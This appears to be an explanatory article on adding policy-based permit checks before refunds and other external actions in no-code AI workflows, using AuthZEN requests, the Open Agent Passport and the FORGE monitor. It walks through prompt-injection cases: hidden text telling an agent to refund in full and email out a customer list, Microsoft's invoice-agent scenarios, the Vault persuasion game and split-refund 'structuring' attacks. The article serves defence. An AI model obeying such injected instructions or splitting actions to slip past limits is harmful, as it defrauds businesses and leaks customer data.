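# Permit checks before external actions in no-code AI workflows

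## How a no-code AI workflow comes to act on the outside world

No-code tools such as n8n, Zapier, Make and Microsoft Copilot Studio let people automate office work by arranging ready-made steps in a visual editor instead of writing a program. Tools that also accept small pieces of code are usually called low-code. Many workflows built with these tools now include a language model. The model lets a workflow handle material that no simple rule could sort, such as a complaint in a customer's own words, and then act on it by sending a message, changing a record or issuing a refund.

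A permit check queries a separate policy service before an external action runs to determine whether the action may go ahead. If the service returns "allow", the recorded response is a permit for that one request. The case for such a check depends on what happens during a run, especially how much of it nobody has decided beforehand.

### From trigger to external action

A workflow consists of steps, which n8n calls nodes and Make calls modules. *Node types*, n8n's node reference, divides operations into triggers, which start the workflow when something happens in a service, and actions, which perform specific tasks. Each step passes its output to the next. According to Mintlify-hosted documentation of n8n's code, n8n passes this data as items with named fields in JSON, a text format for structured data, plus any attached files.

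Some steps only rearrange data inside the tool, while others reach an outside service, such as Gmail or a payment provider, through a ready-made component called a connector. The provider accepts refund orders only from authorized users, so the connector presents a credential, which is a stored key or login. n8n encrypts credentials in its database and lets only certain types of node request them. This protects the key against theft but doesn't control how a legitimate step uses it, so the provider receives the same valid credential even when a step orders the wrong refund.

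An external action is an operation that changes something outside the workflow tool, such as sending an email or transferring money. Deleting the workflow afterward does not recall the email or return the money.

An online shop could use a workflow to handle refund requests sent to its support mailbox. A new email triggers the workflow, a model reads the complaint, a payment connector refunds the customer, and an email connector confirms the refund. Someone on the support team could build this from four or five steps, in either of two quite different ways.

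### Fixed steps and tool calls

In the first version, the builder sets the order of all the steps. The model reads the email and fills in an order number and an amount, then the payment step runs, then the confirmation. The payment is a fixed step, so it always runs at its place in the workflow, whatever the model writes. n8n's *What agents do* contrasts a chain, n8n's term for a fixed series of calls to AI components, with an agent, in which a language model determines which actions to take.

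The second version uses an agent. The builder connects the payment connector and the email connector to a model as tools, writes some instructions about complaints, and leaves the choice of steps to the model. To use a tool, the model writes a tool call, with arguments that specify the details of the request, such as which order to refund, how much and to whom. KNIME's *Agents*, from another maker of visual workflow software, describes this process as a loop. The model starts from the task and chooses either to call a tool or to answer. After each call, it receives the result and chooses again, until it answers. On one complaint, the model might look up the order, issue the refund, read the payment provider's reply and send the confirmation. On the next, it might send an apology without a refund, or refund the same order twice because the first reply looked like an error.

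The model can use only the tools that the builder has connected. In Copilot Studio, the author must define the actions from which the agent selects, according to Microsoft's *Event trigger overview*. Microsoft's guidance on generative orchestration, the Copilot Studio mode in which a model plans the steps, explains that the planner chooses among these tools largely by how well their names and descriptions match the request, and that names matter most. Giving a refund tool a vague name therefore creates a small risk that the model will select it wrongly.

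For each suitable field in a tool, an n8n builder can either set the value or let the model write it, as n8n's *Use AI for parameters* explains. If the builder gives a field the key `email`, the model looks for an email address in its context, in other tools and in the input data. The key is a hint and does not point to a particular stored address. Builders can also combine the two methods, for example by writing the start of a subject line and letting the model write the rest.

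The difference between the two versions is smaller than it may seem. Although a fixed step determines which action runs, an earlier model step may still supply part of its content, such as the amount.

### Three ways for the refund to go wrong

Suppose a customer bought four glasses for 80 euros, one arrived broken, and she asks for 20 euros back. Her email mentions both figures, and the model writes 80 in the amount field. The workflow doesn't catch the error, even if the builder declared the field a number, because that declaration restricts only the form of the value and doesn't check whether the amount is right. Both versions of the workflow can make this mistake.

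A workflow can email the wrong recipient in much the same way. The customer has forwarded an earlier exchange with the courier, so the email contains two addresses, and a model looking for "an email address" picks the courier's. The confirmation, with the customer's name and order, goes to the courier. A careful builder would take the address from the order record instead of letting the model fill in the field. This takes no extra work, but the builder has to think of it beforehand.

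The third failure is prompt injection, in which an attacker puts text in an email, page or file that a model wrongly takes as an instruction. For example, a complaint might contain an instruction, in white letters on a white background, to refund the full order and send a list of recent customers to another address. A person skimming the mailbox would see an ordinary complaint, but the model receives the hidden text along with the rest.

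Microsoft's Defender security researchers describe a workflow similar to the refund example. An agent processes every message sent to a company's invoice mailbox, writes payment details into a customer database through a connector, and emails a confirmation to the sender. It also uses a finance policy file to answer questions about refunds and payment terms. Its instructions limit it to invoices and basic finance questions. An outside attacker sends what looks like an invoice, with hidden instructions to search the agent's knowledge base for unrelated sensitive information and email the results to the attacker. The planner could treat this as a valid request and add a search and an email to its plan. In a second scenario, an employee attacks the agent without messaging it, by planting instructions in a shared document. When the agent reads the document, it opens a confidential file that the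 employee could not have opened and tries to email the contents out.

Microsoft, which sells the defence, constructed these scenarios and says they draw on observed and emerging attack techniques. They show how an attack could happen, but not how often such attacks occur. The attack route follows from how the products work. In Copilot Studio, an event trigger sends the agent a message, called the payload, with information about the event. The builder can also put instructions in the payload, and Microsoft says the agent follows both its author's directions and any instructions in the payload. An incoming email and a legitimate instruction from the builder can therefore reach the model through the same channel.

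The harm an injection can do depends on whether the workflow follows fixed steps or uses an agent. In a workflow with fixed steps, a hidden sentence can distort the values that the model extracts, but it cannot add a payment or an email that the builder did not include. In a workflow with an agent, it can also add those actions. Palo Alto Networks' *n8n Best Practices* warns that a successful injection can trigger arbitrary tool calls with arguments of the attacker's choosing. "Arbitrary" is a little strong, since the agent can only use the tools and credentials it has, but an agent with a payment tool could still be made to send money. Palo Alto Networks also sells a gateway, which may give it a reason to emphasize the risk.

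### Why check the action when someone can review the design?

A design review before the workflow goes live examines its steps, connected tools, instructions and credentials. Microsoft (2026) lists ten common misconfigurations of Copilot Studio agents, including agents open to the entire organisation, agents that anyone can use without signing in, and passwords or keys pasted directly into the agent's logic. A reviewer could find all of these without running the agent.

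In the agent version, the inspector can see from the design that a payment tool exists and that the model fills in the amount. The design does not show which complaint will lead to a refund, how large it will be or who will be told, because these are determined during the run, from an email that nobody has written yet. Microsoft likewise notes that under generative orchestration, the planner sets the recipient and content of outgoing mail at runtime. A bad outcome does not imply a defect that a better review would have caught. As Microsoft observes in a discussion of security risks in agents, an autonomous system can be "working as designed" and still take steps that a person would be unlikely to approve.

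Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) base their whole analysis in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a review of 89 sources, on the moment of the tool call. They argue that an organisation should decide whether to authorise each action separately rather than grant broad trust at the start, because the identity, the permission, the request and its origin all come together only at the tool call. They acknowledge that their principles are old ones in computer security. The newer element is that the choice of action, as well as its input, may depend on text from a stranger.

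The argument is weaker for a workflow of fixed steps, but it still applies. The reviewer knows that a refund will follow every complaint that reaches the payment step and can judge whether that is sensible, but still does not know the amount. Microsoft recommends rule-based, step-by-step flows for payments and other irreversible actions. This is good advice because it settles in advance which action will follow, and a check before the action can then examine the amount. Whether that check would catch the 80 euros depends on the company's refund rule and on what information the check has about the glass.

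### Who holds the action back, and who decides

A permit check has two parts. The enforcement point holds the action until a decision arrives, then lets it run or stops it. The decision service evaluates the policy and returns the decision. Security engineers call them the policy enforcement point (PEP) and the policy decision point (PDP). In the refund workflow, the enforcement point sits somewhere between the model's request to pay 80 euros and the payment provider. It sends the details of the request to the decision service, which returns "allow" or "deny" but does not handle the payment.

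The enforcement point needs the decision service's rules to determine which refunds to block, and those rules have no effect if a payment can go ahead without the check. Because the two parts are separate, many workflows can use the same decision service, and a company can change its refund limit in one place.

Copilot Studio and Microsoft's security product Defender show the split in a working system. Before the agent runs a tool, Copilot Studio sends Defender the parameters of the planned action, the outputs of earlier steps and information about the user. Defender's reply determines whether the action runs. In the invoice scenario, Defender blocks the search before the agent has read or emailed anything confidential. Defender looks for signs of attack and does not apply a company's own refund rules, but a refund check would divide the work in the same way.

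The model's instructions are not a substitute for a permit check. A builder can write "never refund more than 50 euros without asking", and the model will often comply. But nothing holds the payment back until the rule has been checked, so the instruction is not an enforcement point. Nor is there a separate decision service, because the model that interprets the rule has also just read the attacker's email. The invoice agent's instructions confined it to invoices, and the attack works by getting the planner to depart from them.

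Microsoft's guidance is not quite consistent here. Microsoft describes the planner as ensuring that each step is within policy, for instance by seeking approval for sensitive actions, but a few paragraphs later advises builders not to leave every decision to the AI. The second statement is safer to build on. Surapani and colleagues likewise hold that the planning model is not an inherently trusted decision-maker and that something else must evaluate what it proposes. Instructions are still worth writing because a well-instructed model should propose fewer bad refunds, but they cannot stop the bad refunds it does propose.

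### Who builds the workflow, and whose authority it uses

The builder is often a citizen developer, an employee outside the software department who automates part of their own job. Microsoft's list of misconfigurations opens with a help desk agent built by someone on the support team. The builder connects it to an internal customer database and decides that users need not sign in because the agent is "only" for internal use. No alert goes off, and nobody reviews it. Microsoft says such agents are surprisingly common but gives no count.

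This person also decides, perhaps without noticing, whose authority the workflow will use. By default, n8n uses a fixed credential, which means the workflow uses the same account no matter who runs it, according to n8n's *End-user credentials*. The alternative uses the account of the person who triggers the run, but n8n offers it only to Enterprise customers, still as a preview, and its supported triggers include forms, chats and manual starts but not incoming email. A workflow triggered by email to a support mailbox would therefore need a fixed credential.

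Event triggers in Copilot Studio also use the credentials of the maker, the person who built the agent, and can use no others. An agent that runs unattended needs working maker credentials for every action that requires a login. Microsoft tells makers on a training page that all actions happen "as you". Administrators can forbid maker credentials, but Microsoft warns that agents started by an event then fail because no user is present to sign in.

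The workflow uses the maker's login because the customer with the broken glass has no account with the shop's payment provider, and should not have one. But if that login can refund any order of any size, so can the workflow, and anyone able to send the workflow an email has some influence over that power. Security researchers call this the confused deputy problem, in which an intermediary acts with authority that the original requester does not have.

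Sharing extends this authority to more people. According to n8n's *Share credentials securely*, a colleague who receives a shared credential can run and publish workflows with it but cannot view the key. Hiding the key keeps it from leaking, but the colleague can still use it to spend money. According to the same page, people who can edit a shared workflow can use every credential in it, including those that nobody explicitly shared with them. A finance manager who adds a payment login to one refund workflow may therefore have given its use to everyone who can edit that workflow. The payment provider cannot tell these people apart because they all use the same valid login.

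## What the check is asked and how rules produce the answer

A shared login does not show who ordered a refund, so a permit check needs other information. The enforcement point must send the decision service a message identifying the workflow requesting the refund, the order, the amount, and the card to be refunded. If that message uses a shared format instead of a private one, a company can replace its decision service without rebuilding the tools that query it.

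The OpenID Foundation, a standards body best known for a login protocol, publishes such a format, the Authorization API, written by its AuthZEN working group. The foundation's members approved version 1.0 in January 2026 by 81 votes to 1, with 25 abstentions (Jordan, 2026, *Authorization API 1.0 Final Specification Approved*). Later documents may add to version 1.0 but not change it. Keycloak, an identity server, documents an endpoint that accepts requests in this format.

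### The request, field by field

Suppose an American customer bought four glasses from the online shop for $80, and the refund workflow wants to return the whole sum. In the format that Gazitt, Brossard and Tulshibagwale, in *Authorization API 1.0*, define, the enforcement point could send this:

```json
{
  "subject": {
    "type": "workflow",
    "id": "refund-mailbox",
    "properties": { "builder": "dana@shop.example" }
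  },
  "action": {
    "name": "refund",
    "properties": { "amount": 80, "currency": "USD", "card": "card_71" }
  },
  "resource": {
    "type": "order",
    "id": "10482",
    "properties": { "original_card": "card_71", "paid": 80 }
  },
  "context": { "time": "2026-10-07T09:14:00Z" }
}
```

The subject identifies the person or program whose permission is being checked, here the refund workflow. The action names the operation. The format has no separate field for arguments, so the amount, currency and destination card go into the action's properties. The resource is the target of the action, order 10482, and its properties hold the shop's own records of that order. The context describes the circumstances, such as the time of day, and is the only one of the four fields the enforcement point may leave out.

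Gazitt and colleagues let whoever uses the format choose the property names, so a policy that reads `amount` will find nothing if another workflow sends `refund_total`. *AuthZen Profile for Model Context Protocol Tool Authorization* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026) addresses part of this problem with COAZ, a proposed standard mapping from a tool's definition and a call's arguments to the four fields. The profile is a draft and covers tools that models reach through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way of connecting models to outside services.

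Even the choice of resource is debatable. On the working group's mailing list, Auto (2026), in *Updated COAZ proposal*, distinguished between asking whether a subject may call a tool and asking whether it may act on the data behind the tool, and acknowledged that some cases need both. For the shop, the resource should be the order, because good and bad refunds go through the same refund tool and permission to call it does little to separate them.

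### Allow, deny, ask a person

The reply contains a field called `decision`, which is either `true` or `false`. The decision service may add a context with reasons, for example one explanation for administrators and another for users.

A denial is easy to misread because the decision service sends it with HTTP status code 200, the ordinary code for success, together with `"decision": false`. The service reserves error codes for requests it could not process. A workflow that tests only whether its request succeeded would pay out on every denial, so the builder has to make the workflow check the `decision` field.

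The standard has no third value for "ask a person". McGuinness (2026), in *AuthZEN Access Request and Approval Profile*, a first draft from June 2026, adds one without touching the two existing answers. If a person could approve the action, the service still returns `false` but attaches an object that tells the enforcement point it may apply for approval:

```json
{
  "decision": false,
  "context": {
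    "reason": "approval_required",
    "evaluation_id": "eval_5521",
    "access_request": { "expires_at": "2026-10-07T09:24:00Z" }
  }
}
```

After the approval, the enforcement point submits the original question again, and only a new `true` releases the action. An enforcement point built before the draft existed ignores the extra object and stops the refund, which is inconvenient but loses no money.

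### Three refunds under one policy

Suppose the shop's manager writes the policy in one sentence. The workflow may refund up to $100 to the original card, must send larger refunds of up to $500 to a person, and may not make any other refunds.

A programmer would have to ask two things before turning this into rules. A refund of exactly $100 fits both of the first two clauses, and the second clause does not mention the card. Read literally, it would send $240 to a stranger's card to a person for approval, while the last clause flatly denies $80 to the same card. The manager presumably meant the original card throughout, and wanted no review at exactly $100. The rules then read:

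1. If the destination card is the original card and the amount is above zero and at most $100, allow.
2. If the destination card is the original card and the amount is above $100 and at most $500, ask a person.
3. Otherwise, deny.

For the glasses, the decision service finds that `card` and `original_card` are both `card_71` and that 80 is below 100. Rule 1 applies, so the answer is `true`.

Another customer returns a $240 lamp and asks for a refund to the card she paid with. The cards match, but the amount fails the test in rule 1 and passes the test in rule 2. The check returns `false` with an `access_request` object, and the refund is held until a person reviews it.

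In the last case, the workflow again requests $80, but to `card_93`, while the order record still has `card_71`. The first two rules both require the original card, so neither applies despite the small amount, and rule 3 returns a plain `false`.

The policy does not catch the mistake with the broken glass, because rule 1 still allows the refund if a model writes 80 instead of 20. The rules also don't compare the refund with the price, so they would allow $100 back on a $30 order. That comparison is easy to add, because the order record contains the price. Catching the broken-glass mistake is harder. A rule can compute the sum due if the support team records the number of damaged items with each claim, but if the damage is described only in an email, a rule has nothing to compare the amount with.

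### Who is the subject?

The subject in the example request is the workflow. A company could also use the builder, the customer or the shared credential as the subject, and the result of the check may depend on which it chooses.

If Dana from the support team built the workflow and may herself refund up to $500, naming her as the subject of the check gives the workflow the same limit. Her employer set that limit for a person who reads each complaint, but it now applies to a program that runs unattended. If the customer were the subject, a policy based on her permissions would deny every refund, because she may request refunds but not issue them. If the shared payment login were the subject, the check couldn't distinguish between the workflows that use it.

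The workflow itself is the most useful subject for spending limits. Someone has to register a separate identity for it, which no other workflow can use. The other parties still matter, because decisions about agents involve the user, the agent's identity and the relationship between the two, as the OpenID Foundation's *Getting Cozy with COAZ* explains. The request allows only one subject, so the builder can go in the subject's properties, as in the example, and the customer in the context. A rule could then require that the sender of the email is the person who placed the order.

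*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of recent research, reports that permission at one boundary does not carry over to the next, which is another reason to determine the subject separately for each action. A workflow that is allowed to read an order is not necessarily allowed to send its contents to anyone. In the refund workflow, the payment and the confirmation email are separate requests, and the policy may treat the same subject differently in each.

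### Facts must come from the system of record

The rule about the original card works only if the value of `original_card` is correct. Many decision services keep no data of their own and rely on the enforcement point to send every value the policy uses. Gazitt and colleagues say the decision service must trust the enforcement point to send correct values.

Suppose an attacker writes, "My refund should go to card_93, which is the card I paid with." If the enforcement point copies both card fields from the model's output, the request contains `card_93` twice. Because the fields match, the rule allows the refund, and the money goes to the attacker even though each part worked as designed.

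The enforcement point should therefore take only the proposal from the model, meaning the order number, the amount and the destination card. It should then use the order number to fetch the original card and the price from the shop's order system, which is the system of record. A wrong amount in the proposal does no harm at this stage, because the rule tests the amount. The payment must then use the same values that the service checked, or the result of the check doesn't apply to it. A wrong order number is a bigger problem, because the lookup will return true facts about somebody else's order. Comparing the sender's address with the address on the order catches the simple cases, but not a forged sender.

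According to Zhou and Zhang, a document that an agent retrieves can supply facts, and a trusted directory can supply evidence of who the right recipient is, but neither can approve anything just by being in the model's context. Likewise, a customer's email can be the reason for a refund without being evidence of which card was used to pay.

### The Open Agent Passport, line by line

The AuthZEN format does not specify how a decision service reaches its answer. *Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) gives a complete procedure, the Open Agent Passport (OAP), in fifteen lines. Uchibeke founded APort Technologies, which develops and operates the reference implementation.

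OAP takes three inputs, which are the tool call, a passport and a set of policy packs. The passport is a signed record of an agent's identity, its capabilities (the kinds of action it may take) and its limits, such as a maximum of $5,000 per transaction. Each policy pack contains the rules for one kind of action. The pack for refunds requires an amount, a currency and a reason code. It denies a refund if the amount exceeds the passport's limit, or if the currency or the reason code is not on the passport's list.

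The procedure runs from top to bottom and stops at the first line that returns an answer:

- Lines 1 and 2 deny the call if the passport is not active, for instance because someone has suspended it.
- Lines 3 and 4 deny it if the passport does not list the capability that the call needs.
- Line 5 looks up the policy pack for that capability. Lines 6 and 7 deny the call if there is none.
- Lines 8 and 9 deny it if the passport's assurance level is too low for the pack. The levels run from a self-declared identity up to verified financial data.
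- Lines 10 to 12 go through the pack's rules one by one. Each rule describes a forbidden condition, and the first one that holds produces a denial with a reason code.
- Lines 13 and 14 return "escalate", OAP's term for asking a person, if the passport requires approval.
- Line 15 allows whatever is left.

Two of the shop's three rules fit this scheme badly. If the passport's limit is $100, the $240 refund fails at line 12 and never reaches a person. If the limit is $500, the refund reaches line 13, but the approval setting there belongs to the passport and does not depend on the amount, so either every refund that passes the rules goes to a person or none does. The shop could work around this with separate passports for small and large refunds. Escalation is specified, but the reference implementation does not yet include it, and Uchibeke writes that companies that need approvals build them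 into their own applications.

OAP allows its rules to compare the call's parameters with the passport's limits but not to consult outside data, so they cannot look up an order. Before the rules can compare cards, some other component has to fetch the original card and add it to the parameters. The reason code in the refund pack is unreliable if the model fills it in, because a model misled by a false story will also pick a reason from the permitted list.

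Uchibeke claims the procedure has five properties. The same inputs always produce the same decision (determinism). Every valid input produces some decision (completeness). An invalid passport or a missing policy leads to a denial (fail-closed). No tool call runs without an "allow" (non-bypassability). Every decision leaves a signed log entry (auditability).

Four of these follow from the fifteen lines, provided that the software evaluates the rules correctly and nobody steals the signing key. Non-bypassability depends on the surrounding platform calling the procedure before every tool call, which the procedure itself cannot ensure. Uchibeke therefore presents that result as conditional on trust in the platform. "Completeness" covers only the calls that reach the procedure.

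The check is fast enough for office work such as handling a refund mailbox. In tests of 1,000 requests per configuration, APort's cloud service took a median of 53 milliseconds to reach a decision, including about 15 to evaluate the policy. That excludes network time from the customer's own system. Running the check locally avoids the network delay but took 174 milliseconds, because the reference implementation starts a separate Python process. By comparison, the tool call itself usually takes from 200 milliseconds to several seconds.

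### What 4,437 decisions show

APort also tested OAP in a public game called Vault, where participants tried to talk an AI banking agent into making unauthorized transfers. The prize for beating the hardest of five tiers was $5,000. By March 2026 the game had produced 4,437 authorization decisions in 1,151 sessions.

The easiest tier had a permissive policy, with high limits and no restriction on recipients. Participants won 588 of 788 attempts (74.6%). In 202 attempts the model never issued a transfer call, and OAP denied only 5 of the 586 calls that reached it. The hardest tier used the same model with a restrictive policy, and nobody won in 879 attempts. Uchibeke concludes that the policy layer, not the model, determined the outcome.

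That is true, but the zero shows only that the software denies calls when its policy is to deny all calls. Uchibeke describes the strict policy as "zero capabilities, $0 limit". An agent without capabilities fails at line 4 whatever it requests, so no participant could have won by persuasion, and no honest customer could have moved any money.

A later passage describes the strict policy differently, as permitting transfers to approved recipients within set limits, which would be a much better test. The published counts don't show which description is right. OAP denied all 1,911 calls that reached it in the hardest tier. Only 1,453 denials in the whole game were for a missing capability, and 150 of the hardest tier's denials were for malformed requests. At least 308 calls in that tier must therefore have been denied for some other reason, which is hard to explain if the agent had no capabilities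 at all. Perhaps the policy changed during the game.

Participants also chose their own tiers, so the two groups may have differed. This probably did not inflate OAP's results, since Uchibeke reports that the hardest tier drew the more persistent attackers. However, the attackers did not know the policy, and most relied on persuasion rather than technical attacks on the software.

Results from the three middle tiers would be more useful for judging a usable policy, because the rules in those tiers let some transfers through. Uchibeke gives no success rates for them. By subtraction, OAP made 1,940 decisions in those tiers and allowed 1,437. A shop would want to know how many of the allowed transfers were wins for an attacker, and that figure may appear in the companion paper that Uchibeke announces.

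In the trial, about three in four attempts to persuade a current model to use its transfer tool succeeded, which is a strong reason not to rely on the model's instructions to enforce refund limits. When OAP denied a call, persuading the model further did not release the money. Neither finding shows how often a policy that permits ordinary refunds would also permit fraudulent ones.

### Large refunds in small pieces

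Suppose a customer's order came to $560 and an attacker wants all of it refunded. The shop's policy denies a single refund of $560. If the model submits seven requests for $80 refunds to the original card, the policy allows all of them. The seventh request matches the first in every field the rules use, so no rule over those fields could allow one and deny the other. Uchibeke calls this a "structuring" attack, after the practice of splitting bank deposits to stay below a reporting threshold, and lists it among OAP's limitations. The example passport includes a daily cap of $25,000, but the published procedure keeps no running total to compare with it.

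The shop can fix its policy with a small change. The enforcement point fetches the amount already refunded on the order and adds it to the resource's properties, and the rules compare that amount plus the new refund with $100 and $500. The first $80 refund passes, and the second goes to a person because it would bring the total to $160. The total has to be kept per order. A draft of OAP's next version adds totals per agent over a sliding time window, but one agent handles every customer's refunds, so legitimate refunds on a busy day could total more than refunds on a quieter day that included fraud.

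Two requests that should not both pass can still do so if the check reads a total of zero for each before either payment goes out. Zhou and Zhang note a similar condition for Bounded Agents, a research system that keeps budgets across a session. Its guarantee assumes that the system decides requests one at a time.

Running totals do not help when the danger lies in a combination of different actions. In the example of the hidden instruction to email a list of recent customers to an outside address, reading the list and sending an email may each be legitimate. The danger is that this email depends on both a stranger's text and confidential data. The email call alone does not show where its contents came from.

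Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, built a monitor called FORGE for such cases. It records each message, tool call and result during a run and links every event to the earlier events that may have influenced it. Policies are rules in Datalog, a logic language that came out of database research. One of their rules reads:

```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
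```

FORGE denies an action *a* if *a* sends something to an outside recipient, has been influenced by untrusted input, and carries sensitive information. Other rules pass the last two properties from each item to anything that depends on it. If an email depends on a summary, and the summary depends on a hostile document, the email also counts as influenced by untrusted input. The same applies across any number of steps. Before each action, FORGE waits until its record is up to date, gathers the relevant facts and applies the rules. A denial overrides any rule that would allow the action.

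The shop would have to choose its labels carefully. Every confirmation in a refund workflow depends on an outsider's email and an order record, so if the shop labels order records as sensitive, this rule blocks every legitimate confirmation as well as the theft.

Palumbo and colleagues measured that trade-off on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which tool results contain hostile instructions. They compared policies on an agent running GPT-4o, now an old model, whose only other defence was to repeat the user's request after each batch of tool results. With that defence alone, 14.1% of attacks succeeded, and the agent completed 83.7% of its tasks when it wasn't under attack. Adding FORGE with a policy that traces where each argument came from cut successful attacks to 0.9%, but also cut task completion to 62.5%. A stricter policy, which blocks consequential actions once untrusted text has entered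 the context, cut successful attacks to 0.6% and task completion to 33.2%.

τ²-Bench simulates customer service for an airline and a retailer, including cancellations and refunds, so its tasks resemble the shop's refunds more closely than AgentDojo's do. Palumbo and colleagues translated the companies' written policies, which were already detailed, into Datalog rules and tested three newer models. With the rules, average task success rose from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the retailer, although one model did slightly worse in both. The agents received an explanation with each denial and could try again, so they often corrected a blocked mistake. The longer memory did not slow the decision much. With 32 agents running at once, the median check on the airline tasks took less than a millisecond.

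FORGE's guarantee, much like OAP's, holds only if every relevant action passes through the monitor and the recorded facts are accurate. If someone splits a refund across seven emails and each email starts a new run, the record of one session won't show the split, so the shop also needs the total from the order record.

### Could a second model decide?

Fixed rules can use only what somebody has put into a field, so they cannot determine whether a photograph shows a broken glass or whether a complaint makes sense. A second language model could check whether the proposed refund fits the email. It might detect that the workflow is about to pay $80 to a customer who asked for $20, which the shop's rules miss.

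But the judge would also read the attacker's email, and Uchibeke argues that attackers can manipulate a screening model just as they can manipulate the model it screens. Removing the randomness from the judge's output makes it give the same answer to the same email, but this does not help much because the attacker can keep rewording the email. A $100 limit stays the same however someone words the complaint. Rules can also be inspected in ways that a model cannot. Palumbo and colleagues point out that software can search a Datalog policy for contradictions and redundant rules before anyone uses it.

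A deterministic rule can still be a bad one, and if it allows the wrong refund, it will do so every time. Someone must also write the rules. Palumbo and colleagues warn that a language model translating them from plain English may drop a condition or invent one. The ambiguous clause about $100 to $500 could be mistranslated in this way.

The AgentDojo experiments include a rough comparison between the two approaches. One defence had a model read the user's request and select the tools the agent might need, then blocked all others. More attacks succeeded than under FORGE's argument-tracing policy (3.1% against 0.9%), but the agent completed more of its ordinary tasks (73.4% against 62.5%). This defence also had the advantage of a trusted user's request, whereas the only request in a refund mailbox is the stranger's email.

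A check can combine rules with a model if the model cannot override the rules. Zhou and Zhang describe Janus, a system that applies standing rules first and passes the calls they do not approve to an assistant model, which can consult the user. For payments, it seems safer to have the model review the calls that the rules do approve. The shop applies its rules first, and the model then checks only the refunds they would allow. It can send a refund to a person but cannot release one that the rules have stopped. If the model detects that only one glass was broken, a person corrects the $80 to $20. If a deceptive email gets past the model, the shop loses at most what its rules would have paid out without it.

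## A check added as a step in the workflow

In a workflow of fixed steps, the simplest way to apply the shop's refund rules is to add two steps before the payment. The first sends the request to the decision service, and the second tests the answer. Only the "allow" branch leads to the payment. Together, the two steps form the enforcement point. The builder sets it up with ordinary settings and connecting lines, and can make a mistake in either.

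### The Permit.io node for n8n

Permit.io offers a decision service and a community node for it, an add-on that n8n users install from the editor. *Add Permit.io permission checks to n8n workflows* lists three operations. Check tests whether a user may perform an action on a resource. Get User Permissions returns everything a user may do. Get Authorized Users returns the people who may perform a given action, which helps when a workflow has to find an approver.

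Check returns an `allow` field that is either `true` or `false`. The node passes either result to the next step, so the builder has to add an If node that continues to the action only when `allow` is `true`. *Fine-Grained Access Control for n8n Workflows* describes such a workflow for expense claims. When an employee with a $2,000 limit submits a $1,500 claim, the check returns `true` and the workflow emails someone who can approve it. When the same employee submits a $2,500 claim, the check returns `false` and the workflow sends back a rejection.

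Enforcing the shop's $100 limit takes more work than this example suggests, because Permit.io's hosted decision service does not yet evaluate rules about amounts. It can test roles and relationships, so it can determine whether the refund workflow may issue refunds at all. To check amounts, the shop has to run its own copy of the decision service, called an Edge PDP. n8n Cloud, the version hosted by n8n, cannot reach a private network, so a shop that uses it must give its decision service a public HTTPS address and restrict who can reach it. The expense tutorial suggests ngrok, a tool that gives a program on a local machine a public address. A shop that hosts n8n itself can keep n8n and the decision service on one private network.

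When rules depend on amounts, Check sends every field in the incoming item's `body` as an attribute of the resource. In the expense example, the submitter supplies the whole body through the workflow's web address, including the email address that the check uses as the subject. Unless that web address requires a login, anyone who can reach it could enter the email address of a colleague with a higher limit. In the refund workflow, the builder should fill `body` from the order system before the check runs.

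### The same check with an ordinary web request

A permit check is a web request with a short reply, so n8n, Make and Zapier can all perform one without a dedicated component. In n8n, the refund workflow would look like this:

1. An email arrives, and a model extracts the order number, the amount and any card that the customer names.
2. A lookup step uses the order number to fetch the original card, the price and the total already refunded.
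3. A step named `Refund request` gathers these values into one item.
4. An HTTP Request step posts them to the decision service in the AuthZEN format.
5. An If step tests whether `decision` is exactly `true`.
6. The true output leads to the payment and then the confirmation. The false output leads to a message to the support team.

The check returns `false` for both the lamp refund and the refund to a stranger's card, so the workflow sends both through the same output. To send the lamp refund to a person for approval, the builder needs to add another condition that checks for the `access_request` object.

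The key that the HTTP Request step uses to call the decision service belongs in a stored credential. NeuralTrust, which makes a security node for n8n called TrustGuard, warns that if the key is pasted into the workflow itself, n8n stores it unencrypted and includes it in every export. Builders can create the step by importing a ready-made command for curl, a common command-line tool. According to n8n's *HTTP Request*, the import turns every value into text, so a rule that expects the number 80 would receive the text "80". Switching the body to JSON and pasting in the original object preserves the number.

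In Make, the HTTP module sends the request, and a filter before the payment module checks the answer. Make's *HTTP* notes that the module accepts only HTTPS addresses and rejects self-signed certificates. Companies often use such certificates on internal servers, so the decision service may need a new one first. In Zapier, a webhook step can send the request, and a filter can stop the run unless the answer is `true`.

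### Checking text is a different job

Some steps sit in the same place in a workflow but examine text. The TrustGuard node sends text to NeuralTrust's service, where detectors look for problems such as attempts to override a model's instructions. The node then sends the item to one of four outputs: Allow, Report, Transform or Block. Transform passes on a rewritten version, for instance with sensitive parts masked. Each verdict has its own output, so the builder doesn't need to add a separate condition.

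Zapier launched a comparable feature, AI Guardrails, around the end of March 2026. It detects personal data, toxic language, prompt injection and negative sentiment. The builder of a Zap (a Zapier workflow) decides what happens after a detection. Zapier's *AI Guardrails* describes a setting called "Throw Error if…", which stops the workflow when set to True. If it is False, the workflow continues and a later filter can use the result.

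Zapier executive Brandon Sammut called the feature "an actual enforcement layer" in the launch announcement. That is fair for a Zap, since a detection can stop the run. But the enforcement depends on a judgment about text, and Zapier tells customers that the detectors can miss attacks and flag harmless text. It advises them not to rely on the feature alone.

A polite email asking for $80 back on `card_93` contains no insult and no hidden instruction, so a perfect content check would pass it. The permit check denies the refund because the order record lists `card_71`. An angry customer who includes her home address might set off the toxicity and personal-data detectors even though her refund is within the rules. The permit check compares the refund with the order's history and the shop's limits, which the content check doesn't have, and it doesn't use the text of the complaint. The shop could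 use a content check before the model reads the email and a permit check directly before the payment.

### When no answer arrives

If the decision service is down, the workflow either stops the payment (fails closed) or lets it go ahead (fails open). n8n stops the run by default when a node fails. *Catch errors in workflow*, an n8n forum thread, explains that the builder can change a node's On Error setting to Continue or send errors to a separate output. A builder whose workflow keeps stopping overnight has a reason to choose Continue.

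The If step then has to handle whatever the failed node passes on, which may not look like an error. groman's forum report, *HTTP node will not yield error data when continuing execution on error*, describes a case in n8n 1.25.1, now an old version. After a formatting error, the HTTP Request node passed on the item it had received, with no sign of the error. A member of n8n's staff acknowledged the problem and said the node would need changing. groman caused the error deliberately with badly formed JSON, but a quotation mark in a customer's email can have the same effect if the builder inserts the text straight into the request.

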